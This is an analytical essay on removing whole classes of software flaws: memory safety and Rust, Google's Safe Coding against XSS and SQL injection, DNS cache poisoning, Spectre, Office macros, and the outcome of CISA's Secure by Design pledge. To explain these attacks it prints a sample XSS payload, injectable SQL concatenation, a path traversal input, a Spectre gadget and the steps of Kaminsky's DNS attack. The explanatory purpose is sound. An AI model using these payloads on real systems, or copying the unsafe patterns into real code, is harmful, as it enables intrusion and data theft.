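Shane Fry of RunSafe Security put the case against migration to a US House subcommittee. In *Statement and Bio of Shane Paulsen Fry*, Fry (2024) cited an analyst's estimate that rewriting existing software would cost between $40 trillion and $70 trillion, somewhere between a third and two-thirds of the world's annual economic output. Fry added that Rust programmers are too few and command high salaries. RunSafe sells protection for software that its owners don't want to rewrite, so it gains if rewriting looks hopeless. The company had also moved its own product to Rust in about six months.

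The estimate is for rewriting everything, which few people recommend. Fry told the subcommittee that CISA wanted makers of critical infrastructure to rewrite all their C and C++, but in his article for CISA, Lord asks for roadmaps, which might set a date after which a company writes new products or components in a safe language. Fry's claim that automatic tools could do only 5% of a translation is also becoming outdated, since Google's *Scaling Memory Safety* describes using AI to help rewrite a C image library in Rust.

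Google argues for changing only new code. Flaws are concentrated in recent code, because people have had time to find many of the older ones. Google calculates that five-year-old code has 3.4 to 7.4 times fewer flaws per line than new code. In Google's simulation, a company switches its new code to safe languages over ten years and leaves the rest alone apart from bug fixes. Memory safety flaws fall sharply even though the amount of unsafe code is still growing.

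Google found that Rust changes spent about 25% less time in code review than C++ changes, and that programmers had to roll back medium and large Rust changes about a quarter as often. It compared changes of similar size by overlapping groups of programmers, which makes the comparison fairer, but teams may still have chosen easier jobs for Rust. A small manufacturer without Google's training budget can't assume it would get the same results.

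### Devices that nobody updates

The argument for changing only new code is weaker for embedded systems, the computers inside devices such as routers, pumps and cars. Old code becomes safer only if someone looks for its flaws, the maker patches them and the owner installs the patch. Many people look for flaws in Android, but a controller in a water plant may run the same program for fifteen years without an update, so its flaws remain. Fry reported that companies expected some parts of Secure by Design to take 8 to 15 years or more. Aircraft and car makers must also get their software certified, which Fry expects to be difficult in a new language.

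Safronov and colleagues examined 502 samples of router software and found 17,341 occurrences of published vulnerabilities, or about 35 per sample. Memory protection could have eliminated 74% of them. The total counts the same flaw again in each router that contained it, and an attacker can't necessarily reach a known flaw in a library.

Manufacturers can sometimes add Rust to an old system in small pieces. Google's *Bringing Rust to the Pixel Baseband* explains how the company did this in the Pixel 10 phone's modem, which runs tens of megabytes of mostly unsafe code. Google replaced only the code that reads DNS responses, which translate internet names into addresses, because these messages come from outside and are complicated to read. The existing C code calls the new Rust code like any other C function. The first version slowed the modem down and used more power because the build process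 had replaced the modem's fast copying routines with generic ones. The addition takes up 371 kilobytes. The modem had enough room, but Google warned that smaller devices might not.

Hardware can protect C and C++ code that nobody is going to replace. With ARM's memory tagging, the processor gives each small piece of memory one of 16 tags and stores a matching tag in the pointer. When a program frees the memory, the allocator can change the tag, so an old pointer usually no longer matches and the program stops. About one time in 16, the old pointer still matches by chance. CHERI, a research design, goes further by storing the limits of the memory each pointer may reach alongside the pointer, and the processor enforces them every time the pointer is used. Safronov and colleagues compare what each approach requires: CHERI needs new processors, Rust needs new code, and tagging needs less of either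 but gives weaker protection. Both hardware schemes are mitigations, since the flaw remains and the program may crash, but they may be the best choice for an old, exposed program.

Programmers can also write safer C++ by using newer types that store an array's length with its address or free memory automatically when its sole owner is destroyed. These types help only where programmers use them, and C++ still allows raw pointers. A company that adopts the new types without forbidding raw pointers is like the shop that offers parameterised queries but still lets its programmers build queries by joining strings.

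### Do attackers simply move on?

If memory flaws become scarce, attackers may turn to other kinds. Lord cites a Google Project Zero count for 2021, in which 39 of 58 zero-days, or 67%, involved memory corruption. Charrier and colleagues counted 90 zero-days in 2025, of which roughly 35% did. Between the two counts, zero-days based on memory flaws fell from 39 to about 32, while all others rose from 19 to about 58.

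Attackers may well have switched to other flaws, but they had also changed targets. Browsers, which attackers usually break into through memory flaws, made up a much smaller part of the 2025 list. The two counts also come from different teams at Google. The small fall from 39 to 32 is only weak evidence against Rust, since most of the products on these lists had not made Android's change.

A switch would still leave defenders better off if the remaining flaws were less useful to attackers, and there is some reason to think they are. Google has found that memory safety flaws tend to be more severe, more versatile and easier to reach remotely than other flaws. Attackers can also chain several of them to get past other defences, which becomes much harder when few are left. By contrast, a forgotten permission check usually exposes only what the check would have protected, although a missing check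 on an administrator's control panel may expose everything.

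## Which other classes have been removed or contained, and did it take an attack first?

Google's switch to Rust in Android is a single case, so it can't show which of its features mattered. Google has also nearly eliminated two classes of flaw from its web applications. Other makers have tackled whole classes in the internet's naming system, processors and office documents, with mixed results. Attackers had exploited some of these classes for decades, while researchers found others first.

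### Cross-site scripting at Google

In cross-site scripting, or XSS, a website puts outside text into a page in such a way that the visitor's browser runs it as a program. Suppose the online shop shows customers what they searched for, and takes the search term from the page's address:

```
heading.innerHTML = search_term_from_address()
```

Assigning text to `innerHTML` makes the browser treat it as HTML, the language of web pages, which can contain scripts. An attacker sends Ana a link to the shop with this as the search term:

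```
<img src="x" onerror="steal_account()">
```

The browser can't find a picture called x, so it runs the script in `onerror`. Because the script is part of the shop's page, it can read Ana's orders or buy things in Ana's name.

The mistake is obvious in one line, but in a large application the text may pass through several servers and a database before it reaches a page. Google tried training programmers and searching for the flaws afterwards, and found that neither reduced them enough. It then turned to an approach it calls Safe Coding, which makes the compiler reject the mistake. Kern (2025), in *Safe Coding*, explains how this works for SQL injection:

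1. Google defines a new type of text, TrustedSqlString. An ordinary piece of text carries no record of where it came from, and the type supplies one.
2. The functions that create a TrustedSqlString accept only text that a programmer has written out in the source code.
3. The function that runs queries accepts only a TrustedSqlString.
4. An automatic check rejects any direct use of the old query function, except in code that security experts have reviewed.

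In simplified form, the compiler treats three attempts at the same query like this:

```
run("SELECT * FROM orders WHERE product = '" + product + "'")
     // refused: this is ordinary text

q = trusted("SELECT * FROM orders WHERE product = '" + product + "'")
     // refused: product is not written out in the source code

q = trusted("SELECT * FROM orders WHERE product = ?")
run(q, product)
     // accepted
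```

A programmer who has never heard of SQL injection gets an error message that recommends the safe version. A determined programmer could still defeat the check, for example by rebuilding a customer's text one letter at a time from letters in the source code. Kern thinks this hardly matters in practice, because the method is meant to prevent honest mistakes and such code would look odd to any reviewer.

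XSS needed more work because web pages have to include outside text. *If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile*, by Wang, Bangert and Kern, describes how Google's engineers searched the web standards for every browser function that can run text as code, and banned direct use of them. They then created types such as SafeHtml. A programmer can produce SafeHtml from text in the source code, from a sanitiser that strips out scripts, or from a template that neutralises whatever the program inserts. If none of these works, the programmer can ask a security expert to approve an exception.

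Google exempted existing violations so that old programs still compiled without being rewritten first, then worked through the list of exemptions. By the end of 2020, the exemptions covered less than 1% of more than a million JavaScript files. In the early months of the company-wide rollout, the experts received fewer than eight requests for exceptions a week. Google's programmers submit around 10,000 changes involving JavaScript each week.

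Google used to find tens of XSS flaws a year in each large application, such as Gmail. By 2024, the yearly total for all applications built on its hardened frameworks was in the low single digits, and Kern gives a recent average of less than one report a year across hundreds of applications. Applications that use the new database interface have had no reported SQL injection flaw for more than a decade.

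These are Google's own figures, and they count only reported flaws. But Google's *Secure by Design*, an account of its web frameworks, shows that XSS reports fell while Google increased its rewards and launched more applications, which gave outsiders more reason to look for flaws.

Wang and colleagues also followed one product whose team spent about a year converting its code. In the year before the conversion, the product had ten XSS flaws of the kind that arise in browser code. It had two during the conversion and one in the year after. The team was an early enthusiast, so it may not be typical. The company-wide pattern is better evidence. Old, exempted code made up a shrinking share of Google's JavaScript but a growing share of these flaws, as expected if new code has largely stopped adding them.

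### What the bounties contributed

Google had an unusually clear view of what XSS cost it. XSS accounted for 35.6% of the company's bug bounty payments in 2018, according to Conffab's *Eliminating XSS by adopting Trusted Types*, a talk by a Google security engineer. Nearly half the money went to flaws unrelated to the web, so XSS made up about 70% of the payments for web flaws.

The 2018 bounty bill can't have started the project, because Google had described its safe templates in 2014 and began enforcing the compiler checks on all its JavaScript in the first quarter of 2018. But bounties gave Google a yearly price for the whole class, which a single report can't do, and Google could reduce the price it paid. Google's engineers also used a year's reports of XSS in browser code to test a remedy, and found that a new browser feature would have stopped at least 61% of them. All of those flaws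 had already got past Google's code analysis and security reviews.

Bounty reports are mostly near-miss disclosures. Attackers had used XSS elsewhere. In 2005, a script by Samy Kamkar spread to more than a million MySpace profiles in about a day. But Kern and Wang and colleagues attribute Google's change to the steady supply of flaws, not to an attack on Google. Near misses seem to have contributed to a class-level fix here, though it took many of them.

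### XSS outside Google

Few companies can copy Google's method directly, because Google keeps its code in one repository that rejects code that doesn't compile. For other companies, Google's engineers helped develop Trusted Types, the browser feature they had tested on old reports. A website turns it on by sending an instruction with its pages, and the browser then blocks ordinary text from being passed to `innerHTML` and similar functions.

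Trusted Types can also catch mistakes in other people's code. The engineer who gave the talk had turned it on for an application built with Angular, a popular web framework, and it blocked an XSS flaw in Angular itself.

Chrome has supported Trusted Types since 2020, but the latest versions of all major browsers have supported them only since February 2026, according to MDN's *Window*. That month's Firefox release also introduced `setHTML`, which removes dangerous content before displaying text. Mozilla's *Goodbye innerHTML, Hello setHTML* (2026) presents it as an easy replacement for `innerHTML`.

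Each website still has to opt in to the protection. Browser makers could hardly impose it on every site, because it would break any page that passes ordinary text to `innerHTML`, including the many that do so harmlessly. XSS is now rare at Google but still ranks first in MITRE's general list of weaknesses.

### Kaminsky's DNS flaw

In early 2008 the researcher Dan Kaminsky found a practical way to corrupt DNS, the internet's naming system. When a customer visits a bank's website, the internet provider's DNS server, called a resolver, requests the address from the bank's DNS server and stores the reply temporarily. The resolver attaches a number between 0 and 65,535 to each request and accepts only a reply with the same number. An attacker can send forged replies, but one must contain the right number and arrive before the real reply.

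Researchers already knew about this weakness, as CERT Coordination Center's *Multiple DNS implementations vulnerable to cache poisoning* (2008) acknowledged. The usual obstacle was that after a failed attempt the resolver stored the real answer, and the attacker had to wait for it to expire. Kaminsky's method avoids the wait:

1. The attacker asks the resolver for a name that nobody has looked up, such as `a1.bank.example`.
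2. The attacker sends a burst of forged answers, each with a different number.
3. If one matches, the resolver accepts it, together with an extra record that gives a false address for the bank.
4. If none matches, the attacker asks for `a2.bank.example` and tries again at once.

If 100 forged answers arrive in time on each attempt and the attacker makes ten attempts a second (both figures are invented), the attack succeeds on average after about 655 attempts, or a little over a minute.

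The weakness was in the DNS standard, so it affected products from many companies. Kaminsky told a small group about it in March. CERT, a security team at Carnegie Mellon University, then contacted about 150 vendors (Faber, *Responsible Disclosure*, 2008). On 8 July they announced the flaw and released patches together. ISC, which maintains the widely used DNS server BIND, listed no known attacks in *CVE-2008-1447* (2008), so this was a near-miss disclosure.

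The patches made resolvers send each question from a randomly chosen port, a numbered channel that the answer must come back to. The attacker now had to guess the port as well as the question's ID number. Faber estimated that there were around 16,000 possible ports, which would stretch the one-minute attack to about 12 days. Daniel Bernstein's DNS software had randomised its ports for years, but the big vendors did the same only when Kaminsky's discovery prompted them to. They took just over three months.

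The details stayed secret until the patches were released. Someone leaked them on 21 July, working attack code appeared two days later, and CERT had confirmed attacks by 30 July. About a month after the patches were released, a quarter of the organisations' servers that Faber measured were still vulnerable.

Port randomisation only mitigates cache poisoning, because a resolver still accepts any answer with the right port and query ID. It also works only if both are unpredictable. ISC's *Cache poisoning due to weak PRNG* (2025) disclosed that an attacker could sometimes predict the port and query ID that BIND would use. Amit Klein, one of the two researchers who reported this, had found predictable query IDs in DNS servers in 2007.

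### Why the deeper DNS remedy spread slowly

With DNSSEC, a domain's owner cryptographically signs its DNS records and the resolver checks the signature, so guessing numbers no longer helps an attacker. On the day of the 2008 patches, ISC called DNSSEC the only definitive solution but accepted that organisations could not deploy it immediately.

Seventeen years later, DNSSEC was still far from universal. APNIC's *Towards an industry best practice for DNSSEC automation* (2026) reports 2025 rates of 36% for validation and 7% for secure delegation. As CircleID explains, the 36% reflects how many users' queries go through a resolver that checks signatures, which is largely the internet provider's choice. The 7% is the share of domains whose owners have set up signing.

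One provider can turn on signature checking for millions of customers, while signing requires a decision from each domain's owner. The owner gains nothing from signing when a visitor's resolver doesn't check signatures, and a mistake can make the whole domain unreachable. Setting up signing has often meant copying keys by hand between companies' systems.

Some national registries, including those of Switzerland and Sweden, have automated the work. Registries for general domains such as `.com`, which alone accounts for 42% of all domains, need approval to do the same from ICANN, which coordinates internet names. Port randomisation may also have slowed DNSSEC adoption by making the problem less urgent. The spread of encrypted web connections may have had the same effect, since browsers usually warn visitors who reach an impostor's address.

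### Spectre and Meltdown

Modern processors save time by predicting what a program will do next. If the answer to a condition isn't ready, the processor carries on along the likelier path and discards the work if the prediction turns out to be wrong. In January 2018 researchers disclosed two ways of stealing data through this habit, Spectre and Meltdown. Take a program with a perfectly good bounds check:

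```
if (i < length)
    x = table[data[i] * 4096]
```

1. The attacker runs the program many times with acceptable values of `i`, so the processor comes to predict that the check will pass.
2. The attacker supplies a value of `i` that points beyond `data`, to a secret.
3. Before the check is finished, the processor reads the secret and uses it to choose which part of `table` to load.
4. The check fails and the processor discards the result, but that part of `table` stays in its cache, a small store of fast memory.
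5. The attacker measures how long each part of `table` takes to read. The fastest one gives away the secret.

*Spectre Attacks* (2018) presented a new class of attack that works even when the target program contains no mistake for its author to patch. The paper demonstrated the attack by reading all of a test program's memory. Meltdown let an ordinary program read the operating system's memory on many Intel processors.

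Google's Project Zero told the main chip makers about the flaws in June 2017, and there were no known attacks when they became public seven months later. Operating system developers fixed the original Meltdown fairly cleanly by making nearly all kernel memory inaccessible to ordinary programs, and Intel corrected later chips.

Spectre was harder to contain. Before the end of 2018, *A Systematic Evaluation of Transient Execution Attacks and Defenses* had identified six further attacks, four related to Spectre and two to Meltdown. It found that most defences, including some already in use, could not stop every variant. Chip makers and operating system developers tried to keep one program's activity from influencing the processor's predictions for another, but VUSec's *Training Solo* described attacks that work even if this separation is perfect.

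Another variant appeared in August 2026. Many defences clear the processor's prediction records just before a sensitive operation. MIT News' *New type of attack can slip past the defenses* reports that Daniël Trujillo and Mengjia Yan used a precisely timed interruption to contaminate the records again between the clearing and the operation. On AMD chips, that gap is only two instructions long. They read protected memory on a Linux machine at about five bytes a second, fast enough to copy the file containing the system's scrambled root password in half their attempts. AMD released a patch.

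Stopping processors from running ahead on predictions would eliminate Spectre, but few customers would accept the loss of speed. *PerSpectron* (2026) notes that making the processor wait at vulnerable branches cancels the benefit of prediction there, and that several other defences are slow or cover only one variant. Blocking interruptions during the gap that Trujillo and Yan used would probably also slow processors too much. So processor makers keep patching variants of a class that has been publicly known since 2018.

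### Macros in Office documents

Office macros caused harm long before the fix. A macro is a small program inside a document, such as one that fills in a spreadsheet. A virus called Concept spread through Word macros in 1995, and another, Melissa, overwhelmed company email systems in 1999. Microsoft later made Office show a prompt before running a macro, but users could approve it with one click, so attackers included instructions to click in their documents.

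In February 2022, Microsoft announced that Office for Windows would block macros in files from the internet by default. Windows marks downloaded files, and Office no longer offers a button to enable macros in marked files. Users can still remove the mark, and companies can exempt locations they trust. Microsoft began rolling out the change in April, withdrew it in early July after customers complained, and resumed it later that month.

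The security company Proofpoint found that attackers' use of macros in email attachments fell by about two-thirds between October 2021 and June 2022. Much of that fall came before Microsoft's new default of blocking macros reached most users, so attackers probably began adapting when they heard about it. Many switched to disk images and shortcut files. Microsoft had contained one popular method of attack, but attackers could still trick people into running malicious programs.

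### Comparing the cases

The table lists XSS at Google separately from XSS elsewhere, and the two DNS remedies separately, because the flaws in each pair were of the same kind but the outcomes differed.

| Case | Prior harm | Who controlled the point of change | Cost to existing users | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| XSS at Google | Attacks on other sites, many bounty reports | Google | Low, as old code was exempt at first | Under one report a year on hardened frameworks |
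| XSS elsewhere | Many attacks | Each website's owner | Changes to old pages and libraries | Still first in MITRE's ranking |
| SQL injection at Google | Attacks on other sites | Google | Low once Google had built the new interface | No reports for over a decade |
| DNS port randomisation | No known attacks using Kaminsky's method | Many vendors, then server operators | An update, and some loss of speed on busy servers | Attack much harder, but still possible |
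| DNSSEC | Attacks from July 2008 | Domain owners, registries and resolver operators | Complicated set-up, risk of an outage | 7% of domains in 2025 |
| Spectre | No known attacks | A few chip makers and operating system developers | Slower computers | New variants in 2026 |
| Office macros | Attacks since 1995 | Microsoft | Extra steps to run some macros | Sharp fall, with attackers switching methods |

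Harm does not seem to be the main cause of class-level fixes, since Office changed late despite the harm macros had done. Windows has marked downloaded files since 2004, so Microsoft could probably have blocked macros in them more than a decade sooner. The DNS vendors acted within months, when nobody knew of an attack. But harm may still matter. Attackers had exploited XSS and SQL injection somewhere before Google removed them, whereas the two problems that researchers disclosed before any known attack, Kaminsky's and Spectre, led only to mitigations. Both were also unusually difficult to fix properly, so the lack of harm may not be why they were only mitigated.

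Having one owner who can make the change helps explain why XSS became rare at Google but not on the web as a whole. That isn't enough, since a handful of companies design most of the world's processors and Spectre remains a problem. It isn't always necessary either. The DNS vendors had no common owner, but each could randomise its own ports and protect its own customers without waiting for the others, which isn't possible with DNSSEC.

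An easy replacement isn't enough to remove a class either, since SQL injection persists despite parameterised queries. Google also made the old method of building queries from strings unavailable. For Spectre, there is no easy replacement to require.

The explanation that best fits these cases is therefore that a class is removed or contained when an owner can withdraw the unsafe option and the replacement causes little disruption for existing users. Android's move to Rust fits too, since Google could choose the language for new code and leave the old code alone. These two conditions don't explain the timing, though, because Microsoft seems to have met both for years before it acted on macros.

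These are famous, well-documented cases, not a representative sample. There are so few that other combinations of causes might explain them just as well. Successes are probably over-represented, because a company that tried special string types and gave up would have little reason to publish a paper about it.

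## What did CISA's Secure by Design campaign ask for, and what came of it?

Google could ban unsafe interfaces because it controlled the code. CISA doesn't control software companies' code, and Cybersecurity Dive noted in 2024 that it also lacks the regulatory power to make them follow its recommendations. So its Secure by Design campaign, which began in 2023, tried to persuade them to prevent flaws before release. Hundreds signed a pledge to do so, but few have published evidence that any class of flaw became rarer as a result.

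### Persuasion instead of regulation

In March 2023 the White House published a cybersecurity strategy that called for shifting responsibility from users to the organisations best placed to reduce the risk. Six weeks later, CISA and several other American and foreign agencies issued *Shifting the Balance of Cybersecurity Risk*, the campaign's founding guidance. The agencies expanded the guidance that October with more detail on transparency and leadership, according to Bright Defense's *CISA Pledge Adds Vendor Review Signal* (2026).

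Government Technology's *More Software Companies Sign Federal Secure by Design Pledge* summarises the guidance's three principles. Software makers should take responsibility for their customers' security, be radically transparent, and organise their businesses so that staff have the tools and incentives to produce secure software. In practice, CISA wanted products to be safe as soon as a customer installed them and to include security features such as activity logs at no extra charge.

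Three CISA advisers who helped lead the campaign, Lord, Cable and Zabierek, explained its focus on vulnerability classes in *Categorically Unsafe Software*. Aviation investigators, they wrote, look for causes that many accidents share, then recommend changes to training, maintenance or cockpit design. Software makers could similarly group their flaws by class, track each class over time and change whatever lets programmers keep repeating the mistake. Lord and colleagues blamed programmers' tools more than the programmers, so they doubted that training was the best remedy.

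Lord and colleagues also expected that a company could eliminate some classes by itself, while others would need a coordinated effort. SQL injection at Google is an example of the first kind, and forged DNS records are an example of the second. They thought the industry needed better data to tell the two kinds apart.

### Alerts, bad practices and roadmaps

CISA's *Secure by Design Alerts* lists eight alerts from November 2023 to February 2025. Five each covered one kind of coding mistake: SQL injection, directory traversal, operating system command injection, cross-site scripting and buffer overflows. The other three covered default passwords, exposed control panels, and home and small-office routers.

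Directory traversal, also called path traversal, is as simple as SQL injection. Suppose the online shop keeps product photographs in one folder and opens whichever file a visitor requests:

```
show_file("/shop/photos/" + requested_name)
```

A visitor who requests `../orders.txt` gets a file from outside the photo folder, because the two dots mean "go up one folder". The shop can prevent this by numbering its photographs and using the number to look up the file name, so that visitors never supply part of a path.

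CISA issued these alerts in response to attacks, so a near-miss disclosure would not normally have prompted one. The agency did address the wider problem in December 2023, when it asked the public for information about flaws that persist despite long-known remedies. Livesay (2024), in *CISA launches investigation on eliminating recurring software vulnerabilities*, reported that CISA's examples included SQL injection, directory traversal and passwords written into code.

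In October 2024 CISA and the FBI published *Product Security Bad Practices*, a list of practices they considered exceptionally risky in software for critical infrastructure, such as power and water systems. A revision in January 2025 expanded the list to 13 entries. One is putting a user's text directly into an SQL query. The recommended remedy is to enforce parameterised queries consistently, which would be a class-level fix if a maker did it everywhere. Other entries concern individual flaws. For example, CISA asked makers to issue a free patch within 30 days when a component in their product turned out to have a flaw in the KEV catalogue and a fix was available.

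The list also covered memory safety. CISA advised makers not to start new product lines in C or C++ where a memory-safe language was readily available. For existing products, it asked them to publish a memory safety roadmap by the end of 2025, unless they had announced that support would end before 2030. In the roadmap, makers should identify which code they will address first, such as code that handles network traffic or encryption, and show that the plan will significantly reduce memory flaws. CISA suggested writing new components in a memory-safe language and protecting the old ones with mitigations in the meantime, much as Google did with Android.

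The campaign's requests were not binding. Nobody seems to have counted how many software makers published a roadmap by the deadline, though that would have been a fairly easy way to test the campaign.

### What the pledge required

On 8 May 2024, 68 companies signed the Secure by Design pledge at the RSA Conference, a large security trade event in San Francisco. They included Amazon Web Services, Google and Microsoft. The pledge has seven goals:

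1. Increase the use of multi-factor authentication, which requires a second proof of identity besides a password.
2. Reduce default passwords, which are the same in every copy of a product until the customer changes them.
3. Reduce entire classes of vulnerability.
4. Get more customers to install security patches.
5. Publish a vulnerability disclosure policy that tells researchers how to report flaws and protects those who act in good faith.
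6. Publish timely CVE records that include the type of weakness.
7. Make it easier for customers to find evidence of intrusions, for example in logs.

Under the third goal, a company had a year from signing to demonstrate what CISA called "actions taken towards enabling a significant measurable reduction" in one or more vulnerability classes. The company could choose the class, and it did not have to show that the class had already become rarer. The maker of the shop's software could arguably meet the goal by installing a scanner that searches for SQL injection, even if its programmers had not yet repaired any queries.

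CISA had reasons for asking so little. Zabierek told Government Technology that CISA set no deadline for completing the goals because some vulnerability classes are much harder to eliminate than others and finishing could take years. A company that failed to make progress could explain what it had tried. CISA also needed companies to sign. The Center for Cybersecurity Policy and Law's *CISA promotes secure by design principles with industry pledge* says that an industry coalition worked with the agency on the pledge after an initial version came out, and welcomed the agency's willingness to take feedback.

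CISA's *Secure by Design Progress Reports*, a page of links to companies' own accounts, states that the agency "does not enforce nor verify adherence" to the pledge. Six months after the launch, Jack Cable said in The Record's *CISA’s Jack Cable on secure-by-design pledge progress* that CISA could track whether companies published disclosure policies and complete CVE records, but had no single source of data on whether they were reducing classes of flaw. For that, it relied on what companies chose to publish.

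Cable said CISA would not remove signatories that did nothing, because customers would be able to see their silence. The agency planned to publish its own assessment eventually and to find a civil-society organisation to write an independent one, but neither seems to have appeared. Officials also planned to make signatories give up some of the listed bad practices in the second year, but Bright Defense still described the same seven goals in July 2026.

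### What signatories reported

The number of companies that had signed the pledge rose from 68 in May 2024 to 248 at the six-month mark and 367 by July 2026. At the six-month mark, Cable knew of only about 15 reports that showed concrete, measurable progress, equal to 6% of signatories, although every company still had at least half of its one-year pledge period left.

By June 2025, the first 68 companies had reached the end of their year, but CISA's page linked to material from only ten companies. Of the 15 titles listed, eight were about logins or passwords and one was about vulnerability classes. The page omitted Google's report, and material with a general title may contain useful detail. Still, the titles suggest that companies found it easier to report on logins than on whole classes of flaw.

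The table shows what four large signatories reported under the third goal. The entries for Microsoft and Okta come from The Record's *These major software firms took CISA’s secure-by-design pledge*, which surveyed companies six months into the pledge. The other two come from the companies' own reports.

| Company | What it reported about classes | Kind of evidence |
|---|---|---|
| Cloudflare | 79% fewer secrets in code, 44% fewer potential injection flaws | Measured by its own scanner, after signing |
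| Google | Safe interfaces that prevent several classes | Measured results, but from work that began long before signing |
| Microsoft | Standard identity technology to eliminate login errors | Description of activity |
| Okta | "On track" to meet the goal within the year | Statement of intent |

Google's report concentrates on what the company had done over two decades before signing the pledge, including the Safe Coding method that nearly eliminated SQL injection and XSS from its web applications. These are by far the best results any signatory has published, but the pledge can't have caused them.

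Microsoft later reported that its most urgent security work had taken as much labour as 34,000 full-time engineers could do in 11 months. That is a large effort, but the figure doesn't show which flaws became rarer.

Cloudflare, whose network speeds up and protects other companies' websites, comes closest to showing a decline in vulnerabilities after signing the pledge. In *Demonstrating reduction of vulnerability classes*, Pulla, Trishna and Lilly describe how its security team wrote new rules for a tool that scans every proposed change to the company's code. The team first ran each rule without blocking anything to see how many false alarms it raised, then adjusted the rule and began blocking changes that broke it. In the second half of 2024, secrets in code, such as passwords and keys, fell by 79% compared with the previous quarter. Potential SQL and code injection flaws fell by 44%.

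Cloudflare gave percentages without counts, so the 79% could be a fall from 14 secrets to 3 or from 1,400 to 294. The team was also changing the rules of the tool that did the counting. A new rule finds more flaws and a better-adjusted one raises fewer false alarms, so the total can change even if the code doesn't. A fall in injection flaws reported by outsiders would be more convincing.

Still, blocking bad changes improves on patching because it reduces the number of new flaws that enter the code, but it is weaker than Google's method. A scanner rejects code that matches a known bad pattern and lets everything else through, whereas Google's compiler accepts only queries it can verify are safe. In October 2024, CISA's Cybersecurity Advisory Committee, a group of outside experts, similarly warned that many security checks cannot find all, or even most, of the flaws in a class. It suggested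 that CISA support research into measuring whether software follows safe design principles. Christoph Kern, who described Google's Safe Coding method, was on the subcommittee that wrote this advice.

### Attacks on signatories' products

Attackers have continued to exploit the classes CISA named, including in products from companies that signed the pledge. CISA added a command injection flaw in BeyondTrust's remote support software to its KEV catalogue in December 2024, an SQL injection flaw in Fortinet's FortiWeb firewall in July 2025, and the buffer overflow in Cisco's network software in September 2025. CISA's *Secure by Design Pledge Signers* included BeyondTrust and Cisco by November 2024, and Fortinet had also signed by then. CISA had published an alert about each class before it listed the flaw.

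None of these flaws proves that a company broke its pledge. A signatory needed to work on only one class, and a flaw may have been in the code for years before the company signed. Large security and network companies also attract more attackers than most software makers do, so they would appear often in the catalogue even if the pledge had helped.

A fairer test would count reported flaws of each class in signatories' products for several years before and after signing, and compare the change with that at similar companies that did not sign. It would have to separate flaws in new code from flaws in old code, since a company that stopped introducing a class of flaw in 2024 would still be patching earlier instances. No one appears to have done this. Outsiders often can't see when a flaw entered a commercial product, so the companies would need to supply some of the data.

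### Would customers enforce the pledge?

CISA hoped that customers would put pressure on software makers that it couldn't apply itself. In August 2024 it published Secure by Demand, a guide for organisations that buy software. Secure by Demand advises buyers to ask a supplier which vulnerability classes it has eliminated, whether logs come with the basic product, and whether it can supply a list of the components in its software. If enough buyers asked these questions and favoured companies with good answers, makers would have a commercial reason to eliminate vulnerability classes.

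CISA's advisory committee had expected security failures to drive customers away, but it found surprisingly little evidence of this. Thieves stole 40 million card records from Target in 2013, and 11 years later it was still one of America's ten largest retailers. SolarWinds reported over 300,000 customers in 2020, when attackers were found to have tampered with its updates, and still had that many four years later. These are only two examples, and both companies might have grown faster without the attacks. The committee noted that switching suppliers is costly, and that customers often assume a company will improve after a breach whether or not it does.

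The committee also could not confirm the campaign's argument that preventing a flaw early saves money. Many articles cite a study by the "IBM Systems Science Institute", which supposedly showed that fixing a bug during design costs a hundredth as much as fixing it later. The committee traced the name to what seemed to be an internal IBM programme that had not existed since the 1980s. Early fixes may well be cheaper, and most people in the industry think so, but nobody could tell a company how much to spend on them. The committee recommended studying companies' recovery from major attacks over three to five years, and said CISA should consider dropping the economic argument if the study showed no measurable financial harm.

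Even a determined buyer would struggle to compare signatories. As Bright Defense points out, the pledge has no common audit format, so two companies can report progress from different starting points and for different products. Bright Defense sells supplier reviews, so it has a reason to stress the difficulty, but Cloudflare's percentages and Google's history are clearly not comparable.

### How much did the pledge change?

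Supporters say the pledge gave customers a better way to question suppliers and companies a reason to move faster. In CISA's *Statements of Support for the Secure by Design Pledge*, Jason Kikta of the software company Automox called it "an objective mechanism to determine which vendors are acting as responsible partners". Cable thought companies were making small improvements faster than before. CISA also ran monthly private meetings where signatories presented their work to about 150 people, so good methods may have spread without a public record.

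Some evidence suggests that signing the pledge mattered. Okta's chief security officer said that the company found exceptions to its secure defaults while making the commitment, and planned to remove them. In June 2024, Microsoft began publishing CVE records for critical flaws in its cloud services. This went further than the pledge required, but it was part of Microsoft's own security programme.

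Critics doubted from the start that a voluntary pledge would change much. Katell Thielemann of the research firm Gartner did not expect the pledge to change the industry or guide important decisions at the companies that signed, according to IT Brew's *CISA secure-by-design pledge endorsed by dozens of major tech and cybersecurity firms* (2024). Allison Nixon of the security company Unit 221B told Cybersecurity Dive that officials were writing lectures about "bug categories that are old enough to drink". She wanted the government to punish companies that save money now at the expense of security later.

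Bugcrowd, which runs bug bounty programmes, was optimistic about the pledge at first. After six months it complained of an "accountability gap" because many signatories had not published any tangible progress. It suggested that purchasing rules or regulation might be necessary. Bugcrowd sells help with disclosure policies, one of the pledge's requirements, so it would gain from stricter rules.

The critics' best evidence comes from the signatories. On the day it signed, Amazon's cloud business said it was already "well aligned" with the pledge. Fortinet had already eliminated default passwords and published a disclosure policy. If companies sign because they already meet most of the goals, their good record is weak evidence that the pledge worked. Jon Clay of the security company Trend Micro also pointed out that signatories were a very small fraction of the world's software developers, and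 the companies with the worst habits had the least reason to join.

For whole classes of flaw, the critics seem to have the better case. The largest declines, such as the fall in Android's memory safety flaws from 2019, began before the campaign, and only Cloudflare reported a measured decline that clearly came after signing the pledge. The pledge may have done more for login security and CVE records, where a company can make a visible change within a year. Supporters also say that buyers and boards may now ask about vulnerability classes, where they once asked only about patches. That effect is hard to observe, and nobody seems to have surveyed them before and after.

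### After the founders left

The campaign lost its leaders about two years after its launch. Cable left CISA in January 2025, according to MeriTalk, and Lord and Zabierek announced their departures on 21 April without giving a reason. CyberScoop's *Multiple top CISA officials behind ‘Secure by Design’ resign* reported that the Trump administration had made severe cuts to the agency's staff and resources. Bridget Bean, CISA's acting director, said the agency's approaches to Secure by Design would "evolve" but that it remained committed to the principles.

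CISA continued the campaign, although parts of it slowed down. As of September 2025, it had issued no new alert in the series since February. The list of signatories kept growing, and in its *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses*, a bulletin on MITRE's yearly ranking, CISA still told buyers to use Secure by Demand.

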